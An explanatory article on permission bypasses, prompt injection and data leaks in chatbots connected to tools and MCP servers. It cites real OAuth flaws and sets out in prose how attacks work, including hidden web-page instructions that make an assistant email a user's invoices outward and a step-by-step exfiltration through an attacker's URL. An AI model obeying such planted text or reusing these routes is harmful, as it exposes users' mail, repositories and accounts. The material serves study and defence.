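# Permission bypasses, function-calling injection and conversation leaks in chatbot APIs

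## How a chatbot with tools handles requests, permissions and history

A chatbot is a program that converses in text using a language model, which is a system trained to continue whatever text it receives. Many chatbots now also search a user's mail, open web pages and edit files, and they keep a record of what the user told them. The companies that run them also sell access to the models through an application programming interface (API), which lets other developers' programs send requests and get replies. Such a system can fail in several ways. In a permission bypass, an operation runs without approval from anyone entitled to give it. In function-calling injection, an attacker forges or steers the model's requests to outside software. In a conversation leak, the contents of one conversation reach another session, another customer or an outside company.

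Suppose an assistant can read web pages and access its user's mailbox. The user asks it to find the dates on a conference's web page and e-mail them to Ana, a colleague.

### One request from start to finish

The model can neither fetch the page nor send the message. It can only emit text, and some other process has to carry out whatever the text asks for, as OpenAI noted in *ChatGPT plugins* (2023), its announcement of ChatGPT's first outside tools. Here that process is the application, the ordinary code that passes messages between the user, the model and everything else. A tool, or function, is an operation outside the model that the model can ask the application to run. This assistant has three: `read_page`, `search_mail` and `send_email`. The developer describes each one in a schema, a machine-readable statement of the tool's name, purpose and permitted arguments. In the format of OpenAI's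 *Function calling*, a guide for developers, the schema for sending mail might look like this:

```json
{
  "type": "function",
  "name": "send_email",
  "description": "Send a message from the user's mailbox.",
  "parameters": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "to":   {"type": "string", "description": "Recipient's address"},
      "body": {"type": "string", "description": "Text of the message"}
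    },
    "required": ["to", "body"],
    "additionalProperties": false
  },
  "strict": true
}
```

The application sends the user's request to the model together with the three schemas. The model replies with a function call (or tool call), a structured request that gives a tool's name and arguments. Its first call names `read_page` and supplies the conference's web address. The application fetches the page and sends the model a second request, with the page's text attached as the result of that call. Now the model has the dates, and it writes another call:

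```json
{
  "type": "function_call",
  "call_id": "call_2",
  "name": "send_email",
  "arguments": "{\"to\": \"ana@example.org\", \"body\": \"The conference runs from 3 to 5 March.\"}"
}
```

The application matches the name to its own code, passes the two arguments to the mail provider and returns the provider's reply to the model. The model then writes the user a confirmation that the message was sent. OpenAI divides the cycle into five steps: a request that lists the tools, a call from the model, execution by the application, a second request with the output, and a final answer or further calls.

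A function call is only text until the application acts on it, so the application can refuse it. OpenAI's API also lets a developer limit the model to a subset of the tools beforehand, forbid calls altogether or force a particular one. The `strict` setting only makes the arguments fit the schema, and an attacker's address fits as well as Ana's because both are strings. OpenAI also advises developers to leave out any argument that their code already knows, so a refund tool, for instance, would take its order number from the code. OpenAI recommends this to spare the model work, but it also improves security because text the model reads can't change a value that the code supplies.

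### What the model reads at each turn

The model itself retains nothing from one request to the next. After a tool fetches a web page, the model's next input has to contain the tool definitions, the user's message, the tool call and its result. If the user then asks for something else, all of that goes in again. Oracle's *Function Tools in OCI Generative AI*, which documents an OpenAI-compatible cloud service, describes two ways to supply this history. The service can store the conversation, with each new request pointing to the previous response, or the application can accumulate the history and resend it in full. Oracle recommends the first. In the second, whoever controls the application also controls the record of what supposedly passed between user, model and tools. With either method, unless something trims the history, a web page that the assistant opened in the first minute can still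 affect a tool call it writes an hour later.

The model receives these pieces as one sequence of tokens, the word fragments it reads and writes. The chat template is the formatting that joins the pieces and marks who sent each. *TEMPLATEFUZZ* (Shen, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) divides a typical template into five elements: a system message with standing instructions, the user's and assistant's messages, role markers that label the sender of each message, delimiters that separate the messages, and a generation hint at the end that shows where the model's reply should begin. Tool output goes into the same sequence under its own label. The schemas go there too, and OpenAI's service inserts them into the system message. Many templates build their delimiters from reserved tokens, which are single vocabulary items set aside for marking structure.

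The labels mark where a passage came from, but the model's training determines how it treats the passage. OpenAI's *App Security Whitepaper* (2026), which describes ChatGPT's outside connections for business customers, reports that the company trains its models on an instruction hierarchy, so that system and developer instructions take precedence over the content of documents. Such training makes a model less likely to act on a command in a web page, but the model can still do so.

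### From plugins to connectors

ChatGPT's first outside tools were plugins, third-party add-ons that OpenAI launched in March 2023. Each plugin's developer published a manifest, a file with one description for people and another for the model, and ChatGPT placed the documentation of each enabled plugin in the conversation. Iqbal, Kohno and Roesner examined 268 plugins from that June and judged OpenAI's restrictions on them insufficient (*LLM Platform Security*, 2023). OpenAI then introduced custom GPTs, versions of ChatGPT with their own instructions, which reached outside services through "actions" designed much like plugins. It barred new plugin conversations from 19 March 2024 and let existing ones run until 9 April (*Plugin Store and New Chats With Plugins*, OpenAI developer forum). Also in 2024, Anthropic, the maker of the chatbot Claude, introduced the Model Context Protocol (MCP),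 a common standard by which chatbots discover and call tools on outside servers (Agentic AI Foundation). In 2025 OpenAI adopted MCP and launched connectors, links between ChatGPT and services such as Gmail (Timms, *What Happened to ChatGPT Plugins?*, 2026). It renamed connectors "apps" that December (Drio, *What Are ChatGPT Apps?*). In July 2026 OpenAI reused the word "plugin" for a bundle of apps and written workflows; installing one does not bypass the permissions of the accounts behind it (OpenAI, *Plugins in ChatGPT*). OpenAI is retiring custom GPTs, with standard retirement for business customers due on 11 December 2026 (OpenAI, *Managing GPT access in Enterprise and Edu workspaces*).

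With MCP, the mail company or anyone else can run the example's mail tools on a server outside the assistant's application. The application fetches the server's list of tools, gives it to the model and forwards the model's calls. Since the July 2026 version of the protocol (Model Context Protocol, 2026), no session links one request to the next. A server that needs to carry information across calls can issue a handle, an identifier that the model passes back as an argument. Because the handle appears in text that the model reads and writes, a carefully designed server does not treat it as proof of who is making the request. The MCP project reports close to half a billion monthly downloads of its main software kits, and Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) reports over 950 servers in Claude's directory, used by millions of people daily.

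### What a connection to the mailbox grants

Before the assistant can access a mailbox, the user has to connect it. This normally happens through OAuth, a login standard that lets a user authorize one service to act on their account at another without sharing a password. The user is sent to the mail provider's own login page, which lists the permissions the assistant is requesting. If the user agrees, the provider issues an access token, a secret string (unrelated to the tokens of a language model) that the chatbot company's servers attach to later requests. The permissions are called scopes. OpenAI's *Outlook email and calendar app for ChatGPT* lists separate scopes for reading mail, for reading and changing it, and for sending it, so a connection can allow the assistant to read mail but not send it.

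Scopes are still coarse. Permission to send mail covers any message to any recipient until the permission lapses or someone withdraws it, and the provider cannot tell from the token whether the user asked for a given message. OpenAI keeps the tokens out of the model's input, which makes it hard for an attacker to get the model to reveal one. This does much less to protect the mailbox, because the model only has to write a call and the application supplies the token.

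Tools on Model Context Protocol (MCP) servers follow the same pattern, but the protocol's authorization specification also requires the server to verify that the token the client sends with every web request is meant for that server. Authorization is optional, however, so a server can comply with the protocol without checking any tokens.

### Prompt injection and the confused deputy

The conference page might contain a second paragraph, in white text on a white background, that asks any assistant reading it to look up the user's recent invoices and email them to an outside address. The application would pass this paragraph to the model along with the rest of the page. If the model acted on it, the page's author would have carried out a prompt injection. A prompt injection is text from an untrusted source that a model obeys as if it were an instruction from someone entitled to give one. An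 attempt fails if the model ignores the planted text, so researchers report an attack success rate, the share of test cases in which the model does what the attacker wanted. When OpenAI announced plugins, it disclosed that its testers had found ways for unprotected plugins to perform prompt injection, send fraudulent email and misuse the information they received.

The assistant has just used its legitimate access to the user's mail on behalf of the page's author, who has no right to that access. Security engineers call a program in this position a confused deputy. Every check at the mail provider succeeds because the token is valid, its scope covers sending mail, and the account is the user's.

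Confused deputies can also arise without any planted text. *Securing Model Context Protocol (MCP) Servers*, by the security software vendor Corgea, describes a server that acts with its own broad privileges instead of those of the user making the request, so a user with few privileges can reach other people's data through it. The fix is to make the server use the requesting user's narrower privileges. This would not help the mailbox assistant, which already had exactly its user's privileges and used them to act on a stranger's request.

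### The checks on a call

A person or a program can block the model's call to `send_email` at up to four points before the message reaches Ana's inbox.

| Place | Who decides | The question in the example |
|---|---|---|
| Connecting | The user, the mail provider and, at work, an administrator | May this assistant send mail from this account at all? |
| Approving | The user, or a setting the user saved earlier | May this message go to Ana now? |
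| Calling | The application | Is `send_email` available here, and is the address acceptable? |
| The tool's own server | The mail provider | Is the token valid, and does it cover sending from this mailbox? |

A chatbot may act in a connected app without asking the user each time. OpenAI's *Managing app permissions in ChatGPT* describes settings that range from "Always ask" to "Allow all actions". Choosing a stricter setting does not disconnect the account, and the access the provider granted lasts until the user revokes it.

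The application's check can be more exact than the provider's. OpenAI lets business administrators restrict a tool's arguments, for example so that the recipient field of `send_email` accepts only addresses in approved domains. This rule would stop the invoices from being sent to the attacker, regardless of what the model had read, unless the attacker had a mailbox in an approved domain.

Permission checks can also lag behind changes at the source. Some ChatGPT apps fetch content live, so a user who loses access to a file loses it in ChatGPT at the next query. Others copy content into a search index and refresh its permissions every hour, so the index may still serve a document the user can no longer open until the next refresh. OpenAI also warns administrators that restricting an app's direct actions does not necessarily restrict what ChatGPT retrieves from synced data.

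No person or program in the table has a full view of the event. The user sees the proposed message but may never see the white paragraph. The mail provider receives a token and some arguments, but not the conversation. Only the application handles both the conversation and the tool call, and the basic request cycle doesn't record which passage led the model to write the call.

### Where the history stays

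By now the conversation about the conference also exists outside the chat window. The service's database stores it so that the user can come back to it. Caches hold temporary copies for speed. In March 2023, a fault involving Redis, a program for such storage, showed some ChatGPT users the titles of other people's chats. A prompt cache is a more specialised kind that stores intermediate computation, so the service can answer faster when a prompt begins like an earlier one.

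Memory consists of facts or instructions that a chatbot saves from one conversation and supplies to the model in later ones. These can come from sources other than the user's messages. According to OpenAI's *Google app for ChatGPT data controls FAQ*, eligible information from connected Google apps such as Gmail may help personalise ChatGPT when memory is on. A code sandbox, the closed environment in which a chatbot runs programs, keeps files for a shorter time. The one that OpenAI introduced in 2023 lasted as long as the chat, up to a time limit. A share link gives a conversation a web address that other people can open.

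OpenAI logs the requests and responses of app calls for its business customers. The sample entries in the OpenAI whitepaper contain the user's e-mail address, the search query and the titles of the documents returned. OpenAI keeps these logs for 30 days, but customers can export them and keep them longer. The chatbot company no longer controls any data the model sends in the arguments of a call to an outside MCP server, and OpenAI instructs customers to treat that data as shared with a third party.

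All of these stores need isolation, which prevents one user from accessing another's data and processes. Clearing one store does not clear the others. If the user disconnects the mailbox, the assistant can no longer fetch new mail, but the text of messages it has already read stays in the conversation for as long as the retention settings allow.

### Three attackers

Someone who calls the API directly has an account or a key, and can write fields that users of a chat page never see. These may include the tool definitions and, where the client supplies the history, the results of tool calls that never happened. Writing such fields becomes an attack when an application accepts them from its users and then acts with authority the users lack, as a shop's assistant with a refund tool might. A caller gains nothing by using them to reach their own mailbox, which they can already access.

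An outsider who controls text the model reads doesn't need an account. Such outsiders include the author of the conference page, anyone who can e-mail the user, and the maker of a malicious tool, since the tool's description and results both reach the model. The tool's maker also receives any arguments the model sends to it. Iqbal and colleagues assumed no trust between plugins, users and the platform, largely because unfamiliar third parties write the plugins.

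Another customer of the same service can attack through the databases, caches and machines they share with the victim, without sending any text to the victim's model. They look for a fault that delivers the wrong person's record, or for a clue, such as a faster reply, that reveals what someone else asked. Even a model that resisted every injection would not prevent this, because the fault is in the software that stores and delivers the text.

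## Login and access-control failures when a tool is connected

An assistant gets access to a mailbox through OAuth, an exchange of messages between the assistant's application and the mail provider's login service. Most of these messages pass through the user's browser, so anyone who can get the user to click a link can make the browser send a message of their own. Most of OAuth's checks are meant to catch such messages.

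### A connection that works as intended

In OAuth's terms, the assistant's application is the client and the provider's login service is the authorization server. The client registers with the authorization server in advance. It receives a client ID, which is a public name for the application, and declares the return address to which the server may send users after they log in. A connection then takes five steps:

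1. The user clicks a button to connect the mailbox. The application generates a long random number, the state value, and stores it with that user's browser session. It also generates a second secret, the verifier, and keeps it.
2. The application sends the browser to the authorization server. The link contains the client ID, the return address, the requested scopes, the state value and a hash of the verifier, a fingerprint that does not reveal the verifier itself.
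3. The authorization server compares the return address with the registered one, has the user log in and asks whether to grant the access.
4. If the user agrees, the server creates an authorization code, a short-lived secret that stands for this user's approval. It sends the browser to the return address with the code and the state value attached.
5. The application compares the state value with the one it stored. If they match, it sends the code and the verifier directly to the authorization server, which checks the verifier against the hash from step 2 and issues the access token.

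Checking the state value confirms that the same browser started and finished the connection. Without this check, an attacker could start connecting their own account, stop just before step 5 and send the unused link to a victim. Clicking the link would connect the attacker's account to the victim's assistant, and the attacker could access anything the assistant then stored in that account.

The authorization server should send the code only to the registered return address. If it accepted any address in the link, an attacker could write a link that opens the genuine login page but makes the server send the victim's code to the attacker's website.

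The server must also tie the code to the user who has just logged in. If it takes the user's identity from a field in the request instead, anyone can ask for a code in someone else's name.

The verifier limits the damage when a code leaks anyway, because a thief who has only the code cannot exchange it for a token. This mechanism, called PKCE (Proof Key for Code Exchange), is very important for assistants that run on the user's own computer, since a program installed there cannot keep a permanent password secret. PKCE does not help when the attacker composed the link, because the attacker then chose the verifier too. In that case, only the return-address check and the consent page protect the user.

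### Three failures in ChatGPT plugins

Salt Labs, the research arm of the security company Salt Security, examined ChatGPT's plugins in the summer of 2023. It found one flaw in ChatGPT itself and two kinds of flaw in the plugins' login systems (Carmel, 2024, *Security Flaws within ChatGPT Ecosystem Allowed Access to Accounts On Third-Party Websites*).

ChatGPT used a state value that was not random, so an attacker could guess it. When a user approved a new plugin, the plugin's website sent the browser back to ChatGPT with a code, and ChatGPT installed the plugin without verifying that the user had started the installation. An attacker could write a plugin that told ChatGPT to forward the user's messages. After approving it from their own account, the attacker could send the resulting link to a victim. The link led to ChatGPT's real domain, and one click installed the plugin without asking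 for confirmation. According to Carmel, many developers leave this check out because they see no security problem in logging a victim in with the attacker's credentials.

The second flaw was in PluginLab, a framework on which developers had built dozens of plugins. One of them, AskTheCode, answered questions about a user's repositories on GitHub, a service where programmers store source code. AskTheCode kept an account for each user that held their GitHub credentials. During installation, the browser sent a member ID to PluginLab's server and requested a code. The server issued a code for any ID without checking that the request came from that member. Each ID was a standard hash of the member's e-mail address, so anyone who knew the address could compute it. With the victim's code, an attacker could install AskTheCode in their own ChatGPT account and ask it for the victim's private repositories,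 without the victim clicking anything. Carmel demonstrated the attack by reading a file from a private repository through the attacker's account.

The third flaw affected several plugins, and Carmel used Charts by Kesem AI as the example. Its login page did not validate the return address, so a victim who clicked an altered link would send their code to the attacker. Other plugins checked only the address's domain. ChatGPT's return addresses shared one domain and differed in the path, which contained the plugin's ID, so an attacker could substitute the path of a plugin they had written and collect the code there.

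Salt Labs reported the ChatGPT flaw to OpenAI on 10 July 2023 and the others to PluginLab and Kesem AI that September. All three companies had fixed their flaws by the end of February 2024, two weeks before Salt published its findings. PluginLab told Salt that it had investigated and found that "no user data has been compromised", and Salt Security (2024) reported no evidence that anyone had exploited any of the flaws. Carmel also asked OpenAI to stress the return-address check in its instructions to developers, which explained how to build the login flow but did not cover its security in depth.

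### The right user and the wrong records

Even a perfect login establishes only who the user is. The server must still check whether that user is allowed to access the requested record, and some servers skip this check.

*XSS Marks the Spot*, by the security company Imperva, describes an access-control gap in ChatGPT's handling of files. Only the account that uploaded a file to a conversation could retrieve it. But once the maker of a custom GPT had published it, any ChatGPT account could download its knowledge files, the reference documents the maker had attached, by supplying the GPT's ID and the file's ID. Imperva classed this as broken authorization.

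It is less clear how much secrecy OpenAI had promised the makers. A public GPT is supposed to answer questions from its knowledge files, so some of their contents will appear in conversation. Nelson's *ChatGPT Exposes Its Instructions, Knowledge & OS Files* quotes a warning in OpenAI's interface: "Files can be downloaded when Code Interpreter is enabled." (Code Interpreter was ChatGPT's tool for running programs.) A maker who left that tool off could reasonably have expected the original documents to stay private. Imperva used the gap as one step in a longer attack that ran a script through shared conversations. It reports that OpenAI fixed the script flaws, one of them within hours, but doesn't mention any change to the download rule.

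MCP servers may use handles to link one call to the next. If a server accepts any valid handle without checking who sent it, anyone who obtains or guesses one can read or change another user's data. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* recommends that the server store each handle under its owner's user ID, take that ID from the verified token, and reject the handle if anyone else presents it.

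Asana, which makes software for managing teamwork, had a more serious failure of this kind. It opened an MCP server on 1 May 2025 so that customers could query their projects from external chatbots. On 4 June it discovered that the server could give users data belonging to other organizations. SANS's security newsletter *NewsBites* attributed this to incomplete enforcement of access control, which limited users to the types of data they had permission to see but let them get that data from other customers. Security Boulevard's *SaaS Security Alert* (2025) lists tasks, comments, team information and uploaded files among the data at risk, and gives Asana's estimate that about 1,000 customers were affected.

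Asana told customers, in a notice quoted by the security firm UpGuard, that it took the server down "to investigate, contain the issue and prevent any further potential exposure" and then fixed the code. UpGuard's timeline suggests that the bug had existed since the launch, which would mean the exposure lasted nearly five weeks. Asana notified customers on 16 June, twelve days after the discovery, and let them request a list of their users whose data others might have read. A copy of Asana's status notice in IsDown's *Outage in Asana* (2025) shows the server offline from 5 to 17 June.

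No outside attacker caused the incident, and Asana described the exposure only as potential. The precise error remains unknown because Asana's incident report gave no details of it, as Lyons noted in *The Register*. Asana later replaced its beta MCP server with a second version and scheduled the beta's shutdown for 11 May 2026.

### Proxies that share one client identity

Many MCP servers hold little data of their own and act as proxies, passing an assistant's requests to another company's service. A mail proxy, for example, is a server to the assistant and a client to the mail provider, so each connection involves two OAuth exchanges, one with each.

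Mail providers often require a developer to register each client by hand, so the proxy registers once and uses a single client ID for everyone. There are far too many assistants for manual registration, so the proxy lets them register automatically, which OAuth calls dynamic client registration. The trouble arises because hundreds of clients registered with the proxy then appear to the provider as one.

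Suppose a user connects a legitimate assistant through the proxy and approves the access on the provider's consent page. The provider stores a cookie in the user's browser recording that the proxy is approved. Later, an attacker registers a client with the proxy, declares a return address that they control and sends the user a link. When the user opens it, the browser goes to the provider with the proxy's usual client ID and the stored cookie. Because the cookie shows that the user has already approved the proxy, the provider skips the consent page and sends the proxy a code. The proxy exchanges this code for a mail token, then creates its own code for the attacker's client and sends it to the attacker. The attacker exchanges that code for a token that gives access to the user's mailbox through the proxy.

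The usual checks don't stop this attack. The attacker registered the return address and chose the verifier, so both match. The proxy is a confused deputy because it uses the user's approval to act for the attacker.

To prevent the attack, the proxy has to get the user's consent itself for each new client before it sends the browser to the provider. The Model Context Protocol requires the proxy's consent page to name the client, list the access requested and show the return address. The proxy must record the approval for that client alone. If the proxy sets the cookie containing its state value before the user has agreed, an attacker can craft a request that skips the consent page.

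Proxies can also send the user to the wrong address after login. While the user logs in at the provider, the proxy needs a record of the assistant's return address, and some proxies put that address in the state value that travels through the browser. Unless the proxy protects this value against changes, an attacker can replace the address with their own. The victim then approves a genuine request on a genuine page, and the proxy forwards the resulting code to the attacker. A proxy can avoid this by keeping the address on its own server and sending only a random reference to it through the browser.

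### Tokens meant for another server

The MCP rules forbid token passthrough, in which the assistant sends the proxy a token for the mail provider and the proxy forwards it unchanged. A proxy's developer might do this to avoid the second exchange.

An access token works for whoever holds it, so OAuth lets the authorization server mark each token with its audience, the server it is meant for. For example, a user might connect an assistant to a calendar server and a mail server that accept tokens from the same issuer. If the mail server doesn't check the audience, anyone who runs or has broken into the calendar server can present the user's calendar token to the mail server and gain access.

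Forwarding the token may also lead the mail provider to assume that the proxy has already validated it. The provider's logs may show the proxy's requests as coming from someone else, which makes a theft harder to investigate. And if the assistant's token works directly at the provider, anyone holding it can bypass the proxy's limits and monitoring. MCP therefore requires two separate tokens. The assistant gets one that is valid only at the MCP server, and the server, acting as a client of the provider, gets another from the provider.

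### What MCP now requires and how many servers comply

MCP's first version, from November 2024, did not require login for remote servers. The March 2025 version added authorization rules based on OAuth, and the June 2025 version added mandatory audience checks. Authorization is still optional in the current version, from July 2026. Servers that support it over the web should follow Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026), which keeps the audience checks and the ban on token passthrough.

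Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) also requires authorization servers to match return addresses exactly. Clients must use PKCE and must refuse to connect if the authorization server doesn't advertise support for it. Proxies with a single client ID must get consent for each client that registers automatically. The document only recommends the state value, whose weakness exposed ChatGPT in 2023, for ordinary clients, but PKCE also helps block codes that an attacker injects into someone else's connection.

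Another rule guards against mix-up attacks, in which a malicious authorization server tries to trick the client into sending it a code that an honest server issued. The risk grows with the number of servers an assistant uses. The client must record which authorization server it is about to use and compare that name with the one in the reply. The protocol recommends that authorization servers include their name but does not yet require it, so a client may still accept a reply without a name if the server did not advertise that it would include one. Model Context Protocol (2026) also clarified that a client must not reuse one authorization server's credentials with another.

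The July rules deprecate automatic registration, though servers may keep it for compatibility. The preferred replacement uses a web address as the client ID. At that address, the client's developer publishes a file listing the client's name and permitted return addresses. To pose as a known assistant, an attacker would have to change the file on the developer's website. The method is weaker for programs on a user's own computer, because their return address is the computer itself and the file can't prove which program is listening there. Authorization servers must therefore show the user the host name in the return address.

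Compliance was poor in the first half of 2026. In *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers*, Zhou, Zhang and colleagues (2026) used security search engines to find 7,973 live servers. Of these, 40.55% offered their tools without authentication, 29% relied on a fixed token or key, and 30.45% used OAuth. Most of the open servers the team sampled looked like tests or demonstrations, but one exposed an internal customer database that its owner had left open by mistake. Anyone who connected could query more than 5,000 records with names, phone numbers and addresses.

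The team then tested 119 of the OAuth servers in detail and found at least one flaw in every one.

| Flaw | Servers out of 119 |
|---|---|
| Anyone can register a client with any return address | 114 |
| The server lets a client omit or weaken PKCE | 81 |
| The consent page does not show the return address | 72 |
| The server does not strictly check the return address against the registered one | 28 |
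| The server accepts a client ID that nobody registered | 12 |
| The server requires PKCE of assistants but omits it in its own request to the provider | 12 |
| The server accepts an altered return address inside the state value | 7 |
| An authorization code works more than once | 6 |
| The state value is missing or predictable | 3 |

The flaw that Salt Labs found in ChatGPT was rare here, while the one in Charts by Kesem AI affected almost a quarter of the servers. (The rows add up to 335, although Zhou and colleagues give a total of 325.)

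The first row needs to be read with caution because the team tested only servers that supported automatic registration. It also had to leave out 316 servers behind strict corporate access controls, which may well be better protected. Open registration doesn't give an attacker access on its own, since a victim must still follow a link and approve the request. It becomes much more dangerous when combined with the flaw in the third row, because a consent page that hides the return address gives the victim little chance of noticing where the code will go.

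Zhou and colleagues tested with their own accounts and did not take over anyone else's. Their reports to the affected companies led to nine entries in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities, seven of which concerned open registration. They blame the speed at which MCP changed. Within about a year it went from no login requirement to a full OAuth framework, and many developers seem to have built just enough of it to make connections work.

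*Exposed by Design* (August 2026) found that 380 of the 414 servers it audited (about 92%) lacked OAuth, compared with about 70% in the study by Zhou and colleagues. The two teams sampled different servers, so the difference doesn't show that the problem got worse. Where servers used fixed tokens, *Exposed by Design* often found them predictable or empty. It also counted 687 tools that, judging by their names and descriptions, run operating-system commands and require no credentials. Neither study reports how many servers check a token's audience, so compliance with the ban on token passthrough remains unmeasured.

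These are ordinary web-security errors that were common long before chatbots had tools. Zhou and colleagues cite a 2022 test by Philippaerts, Preuveneers and Joosen in which 97 of 100 OAuth providers left at least one known threat unaddressed. MCP creates more opportunities for such errors because it connects clients and servers whose developers have never dealt with each other. None of the break-ins required anyone to manipulate a model. The malicious ChatGPT plugin relied on the model to forward messages after installation, but a guessable number was enough to get it installed. With AskTheCode, an attacker who had the victim's code could query the plugin directly without opening ChatGPT.

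## Forged tool requests, weak confirmations and outdated approvals

A secure login establishes which user connected a mailbox, but not who requested each call made through that connection. In May 2023, Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who writes the blog Embrace The Red, showed that text on a web page could trigger such a call.

### A web page that fetched the user's mail

Rehberger used two ChatGPT plugins. WebPilot opened web pages, and Zapier, an automation service, could read the user's mail and files through an OAuth connection. Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT Plugin Exploit Explained* describes the sequence:

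1. The attacker puts instructions for a language model on a web page.
2. The user has ChatGPT open the page, and WebPilot returns its text.
3. ChatGPT follows the instructions and calls Zapier to fetch the user's latest e-mail.
4. ChatGPT writes a short summary of the e-mail and appends it to a web address on the attacker's server.
5. ChatGPT calls WebPilot to open that address, and the request itself delivers the summary to the attacker.

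The user did nothing after asking for the page. The planted text included an instruction not to ask for permission, because ChatGPT sometimes did so on its own. Anyone who can add text to a page can plant such instructions, even without owning the site. Rehberger had first noticed the effect with a plugin from the travel company Expedia, when ChatGPT searched for flights only because of instructions on a web page.

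Rehberger named the attack cross-plugin request forgery, after cross-site request forgery, an older attack on websites. In the older attack, a malicious page makes a visitor's browser send a request to another site where the visitor is logged in, for example to change the firewall settings of a home router. The browser automatically attaches the visitor's cookie, so the router treats the request as the visitor's own. The browser is the confused deputy in that attack, as ChatGPT was in Rehberger's.

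A web page can often make the browser send a request to another site, but the browser normally keeps the page from reading the reply. Forgery between websites therefore mainly threatens operations that change something, such as a payment or a new password. ChatGPT lacked this protection. Zapier's reply went into the same conversation as the attacker's instructions, and the model could copy it into the next call. Fetching an e-mail therefore gave the attacker the private data, even though it changed nothing in the mailbox. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Removes the "Chat with Code" Plugin From Store* warns about read operations in general because ChatGPT offered several ways to send the results out.

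The standard way for a website to prevent forged requests is to place a random secret in its own forms, where a malicious page cannot read it, and reject any request that lacks it. The state value in an OAuth login works on the same principle. This defence has no counterpart inside a conversation, because the same model writes both the tool calls the user wanted and those provoked by planted text, and the application attaches the same access token to both.

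Zapier fixed the problem on its side by requiring an authenticated confirmation. Embrace The Red points out that a plain confirmation link in the chat would not have been enough, because an attacker could have used planted text to make ChatGPT open that link too.

Read-only tools can still leak data. ChatGPT's Deep Research mode works on a question by itself for an extended period. When Rehberger built a custom connector for it, he had to provide two tools, `search` and `fetch`. Embrace The Red's *How Deep Research Agents Can Leak Your Data* explains how data can spill between connected tools in this mode. For example, a search query that contains a line from the user's mail discloses that line to whoever runs the connector.

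### Chat with Code and OpenAI's confirmation rule

After the Zapier demonstration, OpenAI published a rule against plugins that took actions without requiring user confirmation, saying it would reject them. Iqbal and colleagues, who studied ChatGPT's plugins that summer, describe the rule as requiring confirmation for requests that might alter user data. On that reading, a plugin could still fetch mail without confirmation.

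Rehberger then checked how well OpenAI enforced the rule. He downloaded the metadata of all 445 approved plugins and found 51 that used OAuth, which suggested that they acted on a user's behalf or held personal data. He sampled a few and found more that were open to forgery (Embrace The Red's *Plugin Vulnerabilities*). One was Chat with Code, which worked with the user's GitHub account. In his demonstration, a web page got ChatGPT to call the plugin and make all of the user's private repositories public. The plugin was in OpenAI's store even though it did not ask for confirmation. Rehberger wrote that he had contacted OpenAI about such flaws at least four times, with little response, and that some plugin developers never answered his emails.

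OpenAI removed the Chat with Code plugin after what seems to have been an accident. A Reddit user reported that ChatGPT had created a GitHub issue, an entry in a project's list of bugs and tasks, without being asked. Chat with Code and a plugin for reading links were both enabled in that conversation. A few hours after the story reached the front page of Hacker News, a discussion site for programmers, OpenAI withdrew Chat with Code for breaking the confirmation rule, according to Embrace The Red. Neither the mail case nor the repository case involved a known attack on a real user.

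The removal protected only that plugin's users. The rule still relied on each developer to build a confirmation step and on OpenAI's reviewers to notice if it was missing. Rehberger had asked for a check in ChatGPT itself, which would cover every plugin. ChatGPT's current permission settings for apps are built into ChatGPT in this way.

### One conversation for every plugin

Iqbal and colleagues looked for such weaknesses systematically. They started from known attacks on the web, phones and smart-home devices, and listed those that plugins, users and the platform could carry out against each other. Then they read the manifests and interface descriptions of the plugins in OpenAI's store. When a plugin looked capable of a listed attack, they installed it and tried the suspicious function, revising the list as they went. They did not mount attacks themselves.

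| Between | Goals that the most plugins could serve | An example |
|---|---|---|
| Plugin and user | Manipulate the user (37 plugins), collect the user's data (35), take over an account (27) | ChatSSHPlug asked users for the password or private key to their servers |
| Plugin and ChatGPT | Take over the session (6) | With AMZPRO enabled but unused, ChatGPT answered only in English |
| Plugin and plugin | Capture all requests on a topic (14), capture another plugin's requests (12) | Requests meant for the shop plugin Tira went to a third party's plugin, Jio |

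The numbers are counts of plugins with a risky capability, which can result from a bug or careless design as easily as from malice. For example, PDF Exporter had to receive a chat to turn it into a document. In the team's test, the chat included login details the user had typed earlier.

Many of these risks grew because all plugins ran in the same conversation. This let a flight plugin and a hotel plugin plan a trip together, but it also exposed what the user did with one plugin to the others and let one plugin's output influence calls to another, as in Rehberger's attack. Iqbal and colleagues proposed running each plugin in its own sandbox, with a defined protocol for passing information between sandboxes, much as browsers separate websites.

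OpenAI thanked the researchers for the report but said it had determined that the issues posed no security risk to the platform. The researchers answered that users and plugins were also at risk. At least one plugin's developer told them that it too had reported its problem to OpenAI, which could have fixed it but had not.

Today's ChatGPT apps still share a conversation. *Confused ChatGPT* (Wang, Jha and Lin, 2026) tested what a malicious app could do to the others. The malicious app wrote text into the conversation through a function that OpenAI provides to every app. When the user later asked for hotels in Tokyo, ChatGPT used a harmless booking app to search for hotels in Osaka instead. In another version, ChatGPT immediately called the victim app's tools without any request from the user. The paper tested both versions on six ChatGPT models, the newest being GPT-5.5.

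OpenAI says that widgets, the small interfaces that custom apps display in the chat, receive no permissions beyond those that the app's tools declare. This limit does not address the attack by Wang and colleagues. Their app needed no permission in the hotel app because it only had to influence the model, which already had permission to call the hotel app. Wang and colleagues reported their findings to OpenAI. When they wrote their paper, apps could still use undocumented options that made the attack stronger.

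### What an approval has to cover

A confirmation prompt can stop a forged call if the user's click authorizes only the specific call shown. If the user approves the message to Ana, the application should record who approved it, the tool (`send_email`), the exact recipient and text, the connector it will use, and the time. Before sending the call, the application should compare it with this record and then mark the approval as used. If any of these five details is missing or incomplete, an attacker or an ordinary bug could apply the approval to something else.

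Approval has to come from the user through a channel the model cannot operate, as it did with Zapier's authenticated confirmation. A sentence in the conversation stating that the user agrees is not enough, because an attacker can plant the same sentence.

The application should build the confirmation prompt from the call itself, because a model's description of its call can be wrong. A developer reported an example on OpenAI's forum in *GPT-5.5 claims it's trying to call a certain tool*. GPT-5.5 described its call as a shell command, but the call it had written went to a web-crawling tool, with the command in the URL field. The model then attributed the mismatch to misrouting by the application. A user who approved the model's description would have approved a shell call that the model hadn't made.

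A saved approval often covers a tool but not the arguments passed to it, so permission to e-mail Ana becomes permission to e-mail anyone. Willison's *The Summer of Johann*, a review of Rehberger's later findings, describes a more damaging version in coding agents, which write and run programs for a developer. Several of these agents had standing approval to write files, and planted text led them to add more dangerous tools to the approved list in their own settings file. The recorded approval covered this change, though users who allowed file edits would not have expected it to.

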